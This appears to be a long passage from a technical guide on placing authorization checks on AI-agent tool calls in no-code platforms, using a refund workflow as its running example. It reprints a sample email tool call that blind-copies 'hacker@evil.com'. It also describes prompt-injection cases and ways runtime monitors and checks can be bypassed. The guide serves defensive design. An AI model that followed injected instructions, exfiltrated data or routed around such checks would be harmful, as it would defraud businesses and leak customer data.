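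In the refund workflow, the item passed on would be `Refund request`, which has no `decision` field. A test for exactly `true` would still stop the payment, but a test for "anything except `false`" would let it through. The stricter test would also let it through if the item still carried a `true` from an earlier check, such as a check before reading the order. The HTTP Request node also has a Never Error option, which reports success whatever the status code, so an error message from the decision service reaches the If step as ordinary data.

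A similar mistake is possible in Make, where a router splits a workflow into routes with filters. According to Make's *Router*, a fallback route takes whatever fits none of the others. Denials belong on that route, because if the builder filters for `false` and puts the payment on the fallback route, an empty reply or a misspelled field name triggers the payment.

Make's error handlers also need care. The Resume handler replaces a failed module's output with a value the builder wrote in advance, and the run continues. If that value is `decision: true`, the workflow approves every refund during an outage, and Make's *Overview of error handling* lists the status of such runs as "success". The Skip handler drops the affected item, so no refund is paid, but Make also marks this run as a success, and people may not notice that a customer is still waiting.

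The check and the payment should also not be on separate routes of the same router. If the builder has set Make to store incomplete runs, an error stops the item only on the route where it occurs. Make still sends the item down every other route whose filter it matches, which may include the payment route.

TrustGuard prevents several of these mistakes. If it can't reach its service after three attempts, it sends the item to Block unless the builder has turned on an option to fail open. That option covers connection failures, timeouts and a few temporary server errors. Items still go to Block if the key is rejected, the certificate is bad or the verdict is unfamiliar. Empty text, which a wrong field name can produce, also goes to Block because NeuralTrust's service would score it as "allow". n8n's own On Error setting can send failed items to the error output instead, but NeuralTrust says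 that none of that setting's options can send an unchecked item to Allow.

Builders using an ordinary HTTP step have to make these choices themselves. They can end the deny branch with a Stop And Error node, which makes the run fail on purpose. According to n8n's *Handle errors gracefully*, the failure can start a separate error workflow, such as one that alerts the support team.

### Wrong outputs, changed values and second paths

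If the builder connects the payment to the wrong output of the If step, the workflow pays exactly the refunds that the policy denies. NeuralTrust similarly warns that connecting TrustGuard's Block output back to the agent reduces the check to monitoring. Testing one permitted and one forbidden refund would reveal either fault. Testing only a permitted refund would miss the error if both outputs lead to the payment.

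The check may also let every action through because its policy is still in a trial mode. NeuralTrust recommends starting TrustGuard policies in Observe mode, which records decisions without enforcing them, and switching to Enforce mode after reviewing the results.

A payment step can be connected correctly and still use the wrong values. By default, n8n's HTTP Request node outputs only the body of the reply, so the item that reaches the payment step contains `decision: true` and no amount. The builder has to take the amount from an earlier step, with an expression such as `{{ $('Refund request').item.json.amount }}`. If another step corrected the amount before the check but the expression points to the model's output, the decision service approves the corrected amount and the provider pays the original one. A model step between the check and the payment can cause the same mismatch by rewriting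 the details.

Permit.io's documentation contains a mild example of this. Its Check operation reads the amount from the submitted claim, but the following search for approvers uses a fixed amount of $1,500. A builder who copied the example could send a $1,900 claim to someone whose approval limit is $1,500. The longer expense tutorial avoids this by taking the amount from the claim in both steps. In TrustGuard, the evaluated text goes into a field called `guardrailsInput`, while n8n's AI Agent node in its automatic mode reads `chatInput`. With some settings, the agent therefore receives the original text even though TrustGuard has masked a copy.

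Running totals can also be wrong in Make. By default, it runs workflows that start from a webhook in parallel, so two checks on the same order can both read the old total. Its "Process data in order" option prevents this within that workflow by finishing one run before starting the next, but it makes customers wait in a queue.

The check covers only the path it is on. Someone might later add a branch for regular customers with its own payment step, or a retry that rejoins the workflow after the check. Refunds on the new path would bypass the decision service, while the old path would still appear to work. In Make, a new payment route without a filter would run as well as the checked one and could pay the customer twice. Anyone who can edit the workflow could also delete the check.

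### Tool calls inside the agent

In the agent version of the refund workflow, the agent makes the payment, and the rest of the workflow treats the agent as a single step. A check added before this step happens before the model has chosen an amount, and a check added afterward happens when the money has already been sent.

NeuralTrust says that n8n's AI Agent node gives its TrustGuard node no way to step in during the agent's loop, so TrustGuard cannot see or stop the tool calls that the agent makes on its own. The builder can collect the calls and submit them for evaluation after the agent has finished, but this can only reveal a bad refund, not prevent it. NeuralTrust has a component that stops tool calls before they run, but it is for LangChain, a library that programmers use to build agents.

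Zapier workflows have the same limitation. Zapier describes the same kind of loop for an AI step with tools, and a filter after that step can check only the final output.

Attaching the check to the agent as another tool does not enforce it, because the model chooses whether to call the check and what to do with the result. n8n allows this setup for both TrustGuard and the HTTP Request node, but TrustGuard loses its separate outputs, because n8n reads only the first output of a node used as a tool. A "block" verdict goes back to the model as information, and the model can still call the payment tool next.

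In Zapier Agents, the builder adds AI Guardrails as a tool and writes instructions about when to use it. Sammut said that the feature runs "on every single workflow that needs it", but in an agent it runs only if the model follows those instructions. A prompt injection that causes the model to issue a refund could also cause it to skip the check.

### Check and payment in one tool

The builder can close this gap by replacing the agent's payment connector with a sub-workflow, which is a second workflow that the agent can start as a tool. The model still decides when to request a refund, but the sub-workflow runs the check first and issues the refund only if the result is "allow".

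For the shop, the tool could be called `refund_order` and take two arguments, an order number and an amount. When the agent calls it, the sub-workflow fetches the order record and sends the request to the decision service, using the subject the builder entered, `refund-mailbox`. If the service returns `true`, the sub-workflow pays the checked amount to the original card. In either case, it returns the result to the agent, including the reason if the payment didn't go through.

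The sub-workflow always takes the card number from the order record, not from the model, so an attacker who asks for the money on `card_93` cannot get it there through this tool, whatever the model outputs. The sub-workflow should also compare the sender's address with the order, and it should receive that address directly from the email trigger, not from the model.

A clear denial helps the agent explain the outcome to the customer. But a misled agent can respond by requesting smaller refunds, so every check must include the total already refunded on the order.

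Keeping the check and the payment together also makes testing easier. The builder can run the sub-workflow on the three example refunds without a model, and include a run with the decision service switched off. The fixed-step version can call the same sub-workflow, so a correction to the sub-workflow's error settings applies to both versions.

The agent must not have another way to make the same payment. A general HTTP Request tool with the payment credential would let it bypass the check by contacting the provider directly. The confirmation email also needs its own sub-workflow if the shop wants to control who receives it, and the same is true of every other external action the agent can take. An agent with ten such tools needs ten checks, and someone has to build and maintain each of them correctly.

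## A check that the platform calls before each tool

The software that runs an agent can check every tool call in one place, because it carries out the calls, so each tool doesn't need its own check. It holds each call, queries the decision service and continues only if the service permits the call. OAP assumes a platform that works this way. An administrator switches the check on for many agents at once, so the builder doesn't have to add it and can't leave it out.

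Copilot Studio has an interface for this, which Microsoft calls external threat detection. Its main purpose is to catch attacks, but a company can connect a service that applies any rule it likes, including a refund limit.

### Connecting the decision service

A company can connect Microsoft Defender, another security firm's product or its own service. According to Microsoft's instructions, someone with the Power Platform Administrator role sets up the connection for an environment, a separate space with its own agents and settings. The administrator first registers an application in Entra, Microsoft's identity service, so that Copilot Studio can identify itself to the decision service without a stored password, then enters the service's web address and agrees to share data with it.

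The service must accept requests at two addresses, or endpoints. During setup, Copilot Studio sends an empty request to the first, `validate`, to check that the service works. It sends a request to the second, `analyze-tool-execution`, every time an agent is about to use a tool.

A successful `validate` reply shows only that the service is reachable. CrowdStrike's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Collector*, the setup guide for one outside product, therefore ends with a live test in which the administrator sends an agent a message that triggers a tool and confirms that the call appears in CrowdStrike's console.

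### An email with an unexpected blind copy

Microsoft's documentation for developers gives an example. A user asks an agent to email a customer, and the agent asks which one. The user names John Doe, and a first tool looks up his address. The agent then prepares to send the email, but with a stranger's address in the blind-copy field. The request to the decision service, cut down to the essential fields, looks like this:

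```json
{
  "conversationMetadata": { "agent": { "id": "agent-guid" } },
  "plannerContext": {
    "userMessage": "Send an email to the customer",
    "previousToolOutputs": [
      { "toolName": "Get customer email by name",
        "outputs": { "value": "customer@foobar.com" } }
    ]
  },
  "toolDefinition": { "name": "Send email" },
  "inputValues": {
    "to": "customer@foobar.com",
    "bcc": "hacker@evil.com"
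  }
}
```

The full version adds the chat history, the tool's description and parameters, the identities of the user and the trigger, and a `thought` field with the model's explanation for choosing the tool.

The decision service can detect the problem by comparing these fields, because the lookup returned one address and nobody in the conversation asked to send a copy to another. In Microsoft's example, the service replies with `"blockAction": true` and a reason that identifies the blind-copy address as noncompliant. For a harmless email, the service would only need to reply with `"blockAction": false`.

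Some of these fields are better evidence than others. The text in `thought` comes from the same model that put the stranger's address into the call, so a convincing explanation there proves nothing. An earlier tool output is good evidence if the tool read a company record, but the tool may instead have read a hostile document.

Anyone writing such a service should first check a real request for the name of the field that holds earlier results. Microsoft's example calls it `previousToolOutputs`, but its reference table calls it `previousToolsOutputs`. A service that uses the wrong name would have no customer address to compare with the blind copy.

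### The refund rules behind the same interface

Suppose the shop's agent is about to call `refund_order` with order 10482 and an amount of $80. Copilot Studio sends both values and the agent's identity. It doesn't send the original card or the total already refunded, unless an earlier tool fetched them. The shop therefore needs a small adapter that looks up the order, builds a request in the AuthZEN format and passes it to the decision service.

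The adapter also has to invert the answer, because `true` allows the action in AuthZEN but blocks it in Microsoft's format. Copying the value unchanged would allow every forbidden refund and block every permitted one.

The $240 lamp is harder to handle because the shop's policy sends that refund to a person for approval, and Microsoft's interface only lets the adapter allow or block a call. The adapter has to block it, and the shop has to arrange the approval some other way. CrowdStrike's product has a similar limit. Its rules can normally remove sensitive text from a message, but Copilot Studio doesn't accept an edited tool call, so these rules only report the problem and let the call through.

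When the service blocks a call, the agent stops immediately and tells the user that their message was blocked. A refund mailbox may have no user to tell, so the customer could wait until someone reads the logs. Stopping can also leave the work half done. If the refund goes through but the service blocks the confirmation email, the customer gets the money without an explanation. An employee who then reruns the workflow could refund the customer twice, unless the check counts earlier refunds on the order.

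Copilot Studio makes these requests only for agents that use generative orchestration, not for classic agents, which follow conversation paths and actions that the builder arranged by hand. Microsoft advises using fixed flows for payments, but a shop that follows this advice by building a classic agent gets no check from the platform and would need to add the check as a step.

Generative agents can also use topics, which are prepared conversation flows that may contain actions. Before relying on the interface, an administrator should test whether the platform sends a separate check request for a payment inside a topic. Approving the topic as a whole would provide little assurance about an amount that the flow determines later.

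### What happens after one second

The decision service has 1,000 milliseconds to reply, including network time in both directions, the order lookup and the decision. That is plenty for a rule engine such as APort's, but a second language model that reads the whole conversation may need longer.

Microsoft's documents differ on what happens if the reply is late. According to the developer documentation and Microsoft's September 2025 announcement, Copilot Studio treats a late reply as "allow" and runs the tool. The administrator instructions, however, include a setting called "Set error behavior", which covers both late replies and errors. By default it lets the agent continue, but the administrator can choose "Block the query" instead. A note further down the same page mentions only that the tool runs if no decision arrives within a second.

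CrowdStrike's documentation supports the version with a setting, in which Copilot Studio applies the administrator's chosen behaviour after one second. Most likely, the setting works and the other passages describe the default, perhaps because Microsoft wrote them before it added the choice. An administrator can check by selecting "Block the query" in a test environment and connecting a service that waits two seconds before replying. If the agent's test email still arrives, the setting doesn't cover late replies.

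### Eighty unchecked calls or eighty interrupted ones

Suppose a company's agents make 20,000 tool calls a day and the decision service answers 0.4% of them, or 80 calls, too late. Under the default setting, those 80 actions run without a check. If the administrator chooses to block instead, the platform stops all 80, most of which are probably harmless.

Let *N* be the number of late replies and *p* the share of those calls that the service would have blocked. Let *L* be the average loss from a call that should have been blocked, and *C* the cost of interrupting a legitimate one. Then:

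- Allowing late calls costs *N* × *p* × *L*.
- Blocking late calls costs *N* × (1 − *p*) × *C*.

If an interruption costs $5 of staff time and a bad call loses $200, allowing late calls costs the same as blocking them when about 2.4% of them are bad. If only 1% are bad, allowing them, which is the default, costs $160 a day, while blocking them costs $396. But if a bad call could send the customer list to a stranger and lose $50,000, blocking is cheaper once more than about one late call in 10,000 is bad.

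The value of *p* is hard to estimate and may be higher for late calls than for others. If the service takes longer to analyse longer conversations, an attacker could pad an email with text until the reply comes too late. Late replies also tend to cluster. At an even rate of traffic, an hour's outage would let through 833 calls in a row, although the monthly average might still look small.

Blocking affects a larger share of runs than the 0.4% of calls blocked, because an agent usually makes several calls in one run. If each run takes four calls, 20,000 calls make up 5,000 runs, and 80 late replies could interrupt about 1.6% of them.

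For an agent that only looks up delivery dates, allowing late calls probably does less harm than blocking them, because the information can do little damage and customers would notice the interruptions. For payments, deletions and emails to outsiders, blocking is safer, because staff can repeat an interrupted action but often can't undo a wrong one. The setting applies to the whole environment, not single tools, so the shop should put its refund agent and delivery agent in separate environments. A faster service helps under either setting.

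### What Defender looks for

Microsoft Defender checks the intent and destination of each tool call, topic or knowledge search before it runs. *Protect Copilot Studio AI Agents in Real Time with Microsoft Defender* (Cohen, 2025) gives an example in which a hidden prompt tricks a personnel chatbot into trying to send out confidential salaries. Defender detects the attempt and blocks the call.

In another scenario from Microsoft's security researchers, an attacker questions a support chatbot on a public website to find out which tools and knowledge sources it has, planning to extract customer data later. Each question might look harmless alone. Defender detects the probing and blocks the resulting tool calls, which it could hardly do if it received only the name and arguments of one tool.

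These scenarios don't include measured rates of missed attacks or wrongly blocked calls, so a company would have to measure both on its own agents.

A block normally produces an alert in the Defender portal. According to Microsoft's *Protect your environment in real-time during agent runtime*, Defender still blocks suspicious calls if the Microsoft 365 connector isn't connected, but the alerts don't appear in the portal. If the agent runs from a mailbox, no user is watching either, so the only record of the block might be in Copilot Studio's own logs.

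A shop may want Defender to look for attacks and its own service to apply the refund rules. The setup form has room for only one web address per environment, which suggests that the shop must choose between them. *Control 1.8*, an unofficial community guide, describes a separate built-in switch for Defender, so the two may be able to run together. But Microsoft's Defender instructions direct the administrator to the same form that outside services use, so only a test with both connected would show whether this works.

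Cost may influence the choice too. *Defender for Cloud Apps Helps Protect Copilot Studio Agents* (Miller, 2025) reports that a company needs a Defender for Cloud Apps licence for every user who benefits from the protection. The company doesn't need those licences if it connects another provider's service, although that provider may charge for its service.

It is also unclear whether the feature is finished. A Microsoft notice on Itelio's website gave December 10, 2025, as the general release date, but in February 2026 the administrator instructions still carried a preview label and a warning against production use. Petri's *Microsoft Defender Adds Runtime Protection for AI Agents in Agent 365* reports that Microsoft has since extended Defender's monitoring beyond Copilot Studio to supported agents from other makers and agents that run on a user's own computer, once a company has registered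 them with Agent 365.

### Who receives the conversation

Some of the information the check needs is personal. In the refund workflow, a request could include the customer's complaint, her home address and her order record. The agent may send much of this again with each tool call.

Administrators can't choose which of these fields to send. Microsoft describes the data sharing as "not customizable" and advises companies to enable it only if they are comfortable with that. It also warns that outside providers may store or process the data in another region.

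Sending CrowdStrike the whole request may bring the company little benefit, because CrowdStrike analyses only the tool's name and arguments. It could block the blind copy with a rule about forbidden addresses, but it could not compare the address with the earlier lookup. CrowdStrike still logs the latest message, the conversation history and the arguments, unless the customer restricts logging to metadata. The history may help someone investigate an incident.

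If the company runs its own service, it doesn't have to send conversations to another firm, and it can delete the chat history on arrival if its rules don't use it. Defender also avoids adding a new provider, since the data stays with Microsoft. Whichever it chooses, the company should decide how long to keep the logs, because a record of every tool call soon becomes a large collection of customer correspondence.

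### SandTrap, an earlier monitor inside the platform

The idea of a platform that checks its components predates AI agents. In *SandTrap*, Ahmadpanah, Hedin and colleagues (2021) built a monitor to guard against malicious code in three automation tools: Zapier, IFTTT and Node-RED, an open-source tool with a visual editor. People who use these tools often install components or copy code written by strangers, and that code runs with access to their data.

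One of their attacks closely resembles Microsoft's example. Node-RED has a component that sends email to an address the user sets. The researchers changed one line so that it also sent each message to an attacker. The component would still appear to work.

SandTrap runs such a component in a separate JavaScript environment, using the `vm` module from Node.js, the software these tools run on. The module isn't secure alone, because if the platform passes any object into the separate environment, hostile code can follow that object's internal links back out and take control of the platform. SandTrap therefore wraps every object or function that crosses the boundary in either direction. When code on one side tries to read, change or call something on the other, the wrapper first checks whether the policy allows it. SandTrap also wraps anything the code obtains this way, so the code can't reach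 an unprotected object indirectly.

The policies work at four levels:

- **Module:** whether a component may load a software library at all. A component that only converts text to lowercase needs none, so SandTrap stops it when it tries to load one to read a password file.
- **API:** which functions of a library it may use. A Zapier code step may ask for the type of operating system but not for the computer's name.
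- **Value:** which arguments it may pass. The email component may send only to the address the user specified, which blocks the attacker's copy.
- **Context:** which shared variables it may read or change. In a flow that controls water pumps, a component can't alter the recorded level of a tank.

The platform's operator writes a baseline policy once for all components, and builders or users can add stricter rules for particular ones. If no policy covers an interaction, SandTrap denies it. SandTrap can also draft a policy by recording what a component does during test runs, and a person then adjusts the draft. The final policies averaged 185 lines for IFTTT and 260 for Zapier, but 2,650 for Node-RED, whose components interact with the platform in more complex ways.

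Ahmadpanah and colleagues tested 25 harmless and 25 malicious pieces of code for IFTTT, and ten of each for Zapier and Node-RED. SandTrap accepted all the harmless versions and rejected all the malicious ones. Because the researchers wrote both the attacks and the policies, the results show that the policies can express the right restrictions, but not how well SandTrap would stop an attack the policy's author hadn't anticipated.

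The monitor added an average of 4.10 milliseconds for IFTTT and 4.87 for Zapier. Node-RED components took longer to load, but then ran with less than 3 milliseconds of extra delay. The total added delay did not exceed 100 milliseconds in any Node-RED test. These measurements come from local copies of the platforms on a laptop, not from the companies' own servers.

SandTrap is this fast partly because it makes its decisions inside the running program. It doesn't wait for a reply from another server, so it needs no rule for late replies. A Copilot Studio administrator who chooses "Block the query" gets a similar default but has to accept interruptions. However, SandTrap's rules work with the arguments of a call and values set in advance. They can restrict email to a fixed address, but when a model picks a different customer for each message, the right address has to come from somewhere else,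 such as the order record.

### Comparable controls in other no-code tools

n8n gives administrators a way to run their own code when certain events occur. n8n's *External hooks* lists these events, and the administrator's code can forbid an operation by causing an error. Only someone who hosts n8n on their own server can set this up. The closest event to a permit check is `workflow.preExecute`, which occurs before a workflow runs. At that point the model hasn't chosen a tool or written an amount. An administrator might use the hook to refuse any workflow with a payment step outside the approved sub-workflow, but it can't examine the refund itself. The list has no event for a single step or tool call.

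Zapier moved closer to central control in April 2026, when it announced controls that let administrators allow or block apps for a workspace, team or user, in both ordinary workflows and agents (Zapier, 2026). Administrators can also restrict the actions within an app. In Zapier's example, a sales representative may read and update contacts in HubSpot, a customer database, but not delete them. The platform enforces these limits whatever the builder or the model does. The limits apply to kinds of action, so they could stop an agent from issuing refunds but wouldn't allow a refund of $80 while blocking one of $560. They also don't send a request to the company's own decision service.

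UiPath, another maker of automation software, has introduced central checks that administrators can apply without changing individual agents. UiPath's *May 2026* (2026) describes them as a public preview. They apply only to calls to the language model, so they examine text but not the tool calls that follow from it.

Gumloop, a no-code agent builder, comes closest to Copilot Studio's interface. *Your AI agents, your rules* (Brodeur-Urbas, 2026) describes policies that Gumloop evaluates before every tool call by every agent in a company. An administrator writes a rule in plain English, such as a ban on emails to outside addresses, and a model converts it into fixed code. The code either blocks a forbidden call or lets it run and tags it in a log. Companies can set rules for the whole organisation, a team or a single agent.

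Brodeur-Urbas argues that no agent can get past such a policy by persuasion. That is plausible once the code exists, because the code doesn't interpret the attacker's text as an instruction. But the model that writes the code can translate the rule incorrectly. For a ban on outside emails, it might write code that checks only the "to" field, which would let Microsoft's blind-copy example through. Gumloop lets administrators test a policy on past tool calls before they activate it, and this should reveal a rule that blocks too much. It won't reveal the missing blind-copy check if none of those past emails had a blind copy, so the administrator should add an email with a forbidden blind copy to the test.

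## A check at the gateway, the credential or the receiving service

With the checks described so far, the payment login usually stays inside the workflow tool, so anyone who gets around the check still has a working login. A company can instead move the login to a gateway, a separate server that receives the workflow's refund requests, queries the decision service and forwards only the requests the policy allows. The gateway is the enforcement point, and the person who builds the workflow can't edit it.

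### One refund through the gateway

*Outbound Credentials*, a page in Permit.io's documentation, describes a gateway of this kind. For each request, the gateway checks the destination against the policy, adds the right credential, forwards the request, and removes the credential from the reply before the agent receives it. Affinidi describes a similar gateway that keeps each agent's credentials separate, so two workflows don't have to share one login.

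To use such a gateway, the shop's administrator would move the payment provider's key out of n8n and give the workflow a different key, which only the gateway accepts. The $80 refund for the four glasses would then take this path:

1. The model extracts order 10482 and the amount of $80 from the email.
2. The payment step sends both to the gateway's address, along with the gateway key.
3. The gateway identifies the workflow by its key as `refund-mailbox`, and looks up the original card and any earlier refunds in the order system.
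4. It sends these facts to the decision service, which returns `true`.
5. The gateway adds the provider's key and sends the refund request to the provider.
6. The provider pays, and the gateway passes the reply back to the workflow without the key.

If the workflow had asked for $560, the decision service would have returned `false` and the provider would have received nothing.

The shop should confirm that its gateway can do steps 3 and 4. Permit.io's page mentions a check on the destination, which would show only that the workflow may contact the payment provider. To enforce a refund limit, the gateway also has to read the amount.

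When the check is a separate step in the workflow, someone can delete it and leave a payment step that still works. When the payment goes through a gateway that does the check, deleting the call to the gateway deletes the payment too. The provider rejects direct requests because the workflow has no valid key, whether they come from a second payment step added by a colleague or from a misled agent using a general HTTP tool. The gateway also forwards the same request it checked, so no later step in the workflow can change the amount before the payment.

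The gateway check works only if the old key has been canceled. n8n or an exported workflow may still contain a copy, so the administrator should have the provider issue a new key for the gateway and cancel the old one. A builder with a personal login at the provider could also connect that account to n8n and bypass the gateway, unless the company restricts logins and blocks other network paths to the provider. The key that n8n uses to call the gateway needs protection as well, although a thief could use it only for requests that the policy allows.

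### Gateways that carry only model traffic

Many of the "AI gateways" sold for workflow tools sit between the workflow and the model provider. When the refund workflow runs, it sends the complaint to the model provider and receives a reply, which is model traffic. It then sends a refund request to the payment provider, which is action traffic. A gateway on the model connection doesn't receive the refund request.

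The product that Palo Alto Networks recommends to n8n users is of the first kind. It sits between n8n and model providers such as OpenAI and Anthropic, stores their keys, and examines prompts and replies. It can mask a customer's home address before the complaint leaves the company, whereas n8n's own redaction only hides the data in n8n's interface. It can also cap spending on model calls.

The amount of information about a refund that passes through this gateway depends on the workflow. In the agent version, the model's reply contains the proposed tool call, including the amount. In the version with fixed steps, the reply may contain just an order number and the figure 80, with no sign that a payment comes next. In both versions, n8n then contacts the payment provider over a separate connection, using a payment login that is still in n8n. If an employee reruns only the payment step, there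 is no model traffic.

The gateway may detect a prompt injection in an email before the model reads it. But the gateway doesn't control the connection used to send payments, so if it misses the attack, it can't block a resulting payment.

Keel, a product in private beta, makes the difference easier to see because it also uses the word "permit". The example request in Keel's guide for programmers identifies a user, an action called `ai.generate`, a model provider and a model. It also estimates 200 input tokens and 500 output tokens (the small pieces of text by which providers measure usage). Keel's answer therefore determines whether this user may make this model call within the budget, and the request contains no information about a refund.

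A program can send its model calls through Keel's proxy, which evaluates the permit and contacts the model provider only if the call is allowed. Alternatively, the program can request a permit from Keel, contact the provider itself and report its usage afterwards. In that case the program has to enforce the permit decision itself, and someone could remove the check as easily as they could remove a step from an n8n workflow.

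Keel can also limit the number of model calls in a declared workflow. The guide's example sets an expected count of ten calls and a limit of fifteen. This protects the budget if an agent gets stuck in a loop, but a single model call is enough to start a bad refund. The guide includes a filter for permits of type `mcp_tool`, which suggests that Keel has some form of permit for tool calls, but it doesn't explain how a program would request one. Keel's signed records serve another purpose, as evidence of its decisions.

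A product can carry both kinds of traffic. In June 2026, Amazon's cloud division, AWS, added content checks to its AgentCore gateway that cover calls to tools, other agents and models (AWS, *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore now supports Bedrock Guardrails in policy*, 2026). A buyer should therefore ask which connections will pass through the gateway and which keys it will hold. The gateway can't hold back a payment if the payment key stays in n8n.

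### Tools behind a gateway, with rules in Cedar

A gateway for action traffic has to find the amount in each request, but every payment provider has its own format. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) helps because it gives all tool calls the same form. An MCP server publishes a list of tools, with a name, a description and the expected arguments for each. An agent's software calls a tool by sending a `tools/call` message with the tool's name and arguments. A gateway can act as the MCP server, check each message, and pass it on to the service or program that does the work. n8n has MCP nodes, so an n8n agent can get its tools through such a gateway.

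Amazon Bedrock AgentCore, AWS's platform for running agents, includes such a gateway. Its policy feature became generally available in thirteen AWS regions on March 3, 2026 (AWS, *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available*, 2026). Administrators write the rules in Cedar, an open-source language AWS developed for authorization. Setting up the gateway requires command-line tools and a cloud account, so it is work for an IT department. The citizen developer then only has to connect the agent to it.

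A Cedar rule either permits or forbids something. It names a principal (the subject of the request), an action and a resource, and can add conditions. These two rules for the shop adapt examples from AWS's documentation:

```cedar
permit(
  principal is AgentCore::OAuthUser,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"RefundTarget___process_refund",
  resource == AgentCore::Gateway::"GATEWAY-ARN"
) when {
  principal.hasTag("username") &&
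  principal.getTag("username") == "refund-mailbox" &&
  context.input.amount > 0 &&
  context.input.amount <= 100
};

forbid(
  principal,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"RefundTarget___process_refund",
  resource == AgentCore::Gateway::"GATEWAY-ARN"
) when {
  context.input.orderDate.offset(duration("90d"))
    < context.system.now
};
```

The first rule permits the refund workflow to pay back up to $100. The second forbids any refund on an order more than 90 days old. In AgentCore, the action is the tool, the resource is the gateway, and `context.input` holds the call's arguments. `GATEWAY-ARN` stands for the gateway's full identifier at AWS.

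The gateway denies every call that no rule permits, and a matching `forbid` overrides any `permit`. An $80 refund on last week's order passes. The gateway denies the $240 refund for the lamp because no rule permits it. It also denies an $80 refund on an order from last year, which matches both the `permit` and the `forbid`.

AWS's tutorial, *Getting started with Policy in AgentCore*, says that a rule for a specific tool must also name a specific gateway, or AgentCore rejects it. The sample rules in AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* leave out the gateway, so they won't work as printed. The tutorial's refund tool takes whole dollars, so a shop that refunds $19.50 would have to send the amount in cents and write the limit as 10,000.

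For simplicity, the tutorial's gateway requires no login, so anyone with its address can request refunds below the $1,000 limit. The rule doesn't limit the number of refunds, and one hundred requests for $999 each would total $99,900. AWS tells customers to require a login in production, and the first rule above needs one because it checks the caller's username.

### What the Cedar rules can and can't use

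AWS distinguishes between two sources of information in a rule. The username comes from a login token, which the model can't change, while the amount comes from the model's tool call. Letting the model supply the amount is harmless because the rule limits it and the provider pays the same amount the rule checked.

The order date, however, is another argument of the tool call in AWS's example, so a model that has read a deceptive email could write yesterday's date and get an old order past the 90-day rule. The rules above can't look up the real date. The shop could have a fixed step in n8n set `orderDate` from the order system, but someone could change that step. It could also put the lookup in the program behind the gateway, which processes the refund in AWS's tutorial. That program can also take the original card from the order record, as the sub-workflow in n8n did. But part of the refund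 policy is then in the program's code, where the people who maintain the Cedar rules may not see it.

Seven refunds of $80 on the same order also satisfy the first rule, because it applies to each call separately. AWS has since added rules that can depend on earlier calls. AWS's *Temporal policies* explains that these rules use Dogwood, an extension of Cedar that can count actions, add up amounts or require an approval within the past hour. A rule that adds up refunds could block the second one.

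This total covers only one session, and the caller supplies the session's ID. If the workflow creates a new ID for each email, seven emails still produce seven refunds. The builder could use the order number as the ID, but a rule can look back at most 24 hours, and any change to these rules ends the open sessions. The running total in the order system is safer. InfoQ (2026) lists rules tied to clock time among the plans for Dogwood, so daily limits that run from midnight to midnight may come later.

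When an agent requests the list of tools, AgentCore's gateway also leaves out those that the rules would always deny. This mainly prevents wasted attempts, because the gateway would deny those calls anyway. An attacker who knows a hidden tool's name could still put it in an email the agent reads, so AWS goes a little too far when it says that an agent can't attempt to use a tool it doesn't know exists.

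An administrator can type "Only allow refunds under 1000 dollars" and have a language model write the Cedar rule. AgentCore then checks whether the rule refers to real tools and arguments, and uses mathematical logic to find rules that allow everything or nothing. It can also detect when one rule cancels another. In AWS's example, one rule permits refunds under $100 for a group of customers, and another forbids refunds under $500 for the same group, so none of them can get a refund. The shop's manager still has to notice if someone types an extra zero, because a limit of $1,000 is as logically consistent as a limit of $100.

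AWS Greenlight, a preview service, goes further by drafting rules from a company's procedures and logs. Before anyone accepts a new rule, the service shows which recorded calls it would block, according to Help Net Security's *AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules* (2026). Like Gumloop's test on past calls, this preview is better at revealing a rule that blocks too much than one that blocks too little.

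Content checks can feed into the same rules. IT-Online's *Check Point announces integration with Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* (2026) describes how Check Point, a security company, can report signs of prompt injection or sensitive data to AgentCore, whose policy then determines whether to allow the action. The article, which reads like a press release, says that agents can't bypass these controls, but also that the controls apply to "selected agent actions", so the customer still has to select the right ones.

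Two gateways that use Cedar may not offer the same control. Redpanda's *Manage Access Policies* (2026), which covers a preview feature, shows that a rule can permit the support team to call the tools on one MCP server. It lists conditions on labels and ownership but none on the arguments of a call, so such a rule could determine who may use the refund tool, but not how much they may refund. Redpanda also warns that policy changes reach its enforcement points with a delay, which matters in an emergency. AWS gives an example of a `forbid` rule that shuts off all refunds at once. After saving such a rule in any gateway, the administrator should send a test refund to make sure it has taken effect.

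### When the receiving service checks the request itself

A gateway stores a company's logins in one place, so an attacker who takes it over can use them all. The same is true of a workflow platform that stores the logins of thousands of customers. After either takeover, only the payment provider can still refuse a bad refund.

Earlence Fernandes and colleagues addressed this problem in *Decentralized Action Integrity for Trigger-Action IoT Platforms*, a 2018 NDSS security conference paper. Trigger-action platforms such as IFTTT run simple rules of the form "if this happens, do that". To run them, the platforms store access tokens, which are digital passes that a service issues when a user connects an account. A token often permits far more than the user's rule needs, and an attacker who takes over the platform can use those extra permissions.

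The paper's design divides the platform into a cloud service that nobody has to trust and a client program that each user trusts. The user creates a rule in the client, which obtains tokens that work only for that rule. The cloud service receives these tokens and runs the rule. When the triggering event occurs, the service that detected it signs a record of the event. The service that carries out the action checks the token and the signed record, and refuses anything that doesn't fit the rule. An attacker who controls the cloud service therefore can't invent an event or order a different action. The design added only milliseconds of delay, and users didn't have to approve more login requests.

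For the shop, such a token might allow refunds of up to $100 to the card used for the order. An attacker with full control of n8n still couldn't use the token to send $560 to another card. But the payment provider would have to issue and check these tokens, which a small shop can't arrange alone.

An AI workflow also weakens the link between the event and the action. A signed record can prove that an email arrived, but not that the customer is owed $80, because a model worked out that amount from the text. A warehouse scan showing which item came back would be a better trigger, because the provider could then compare the refund with the item's price.

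AgentCore offers a simpler arrangement, which AWS calls token passthrough. The gateway forwards the caller's own token unchanged, and the receiving service validates it. The service can then tell callers apart, but the caller has a token that the service accepts. Unless the service rejects requests that don't come through the gateway, a workflow could send its refund request directly to the service and skip the gateway's rules.

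### What a gateway costs

A ready-made payment connector normally sends its requests to the provider's address. If it has no setting for a different address, the builder has to replace it with a general HTTP step or an MCP tool and fill in the fields by hand. Connectors that log in through the provider's sign-in page are harder to move, because the workflow platform receives and stores the token. A company that hosts n8n on its own server can also try to redirect the traffic on its network, but the requests are encrypted, so the gateway can read them only if the server accepts the gateway's certificate. Zapier runs workflows on its own servers, where the shop has no control over the network.

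These checks remove some of the convenience that led an employee to choose a no-code tool. It makes sense to start with payments, deletions and messages to outsiders, and to leave a connector that only reads delivery dates unchanged.

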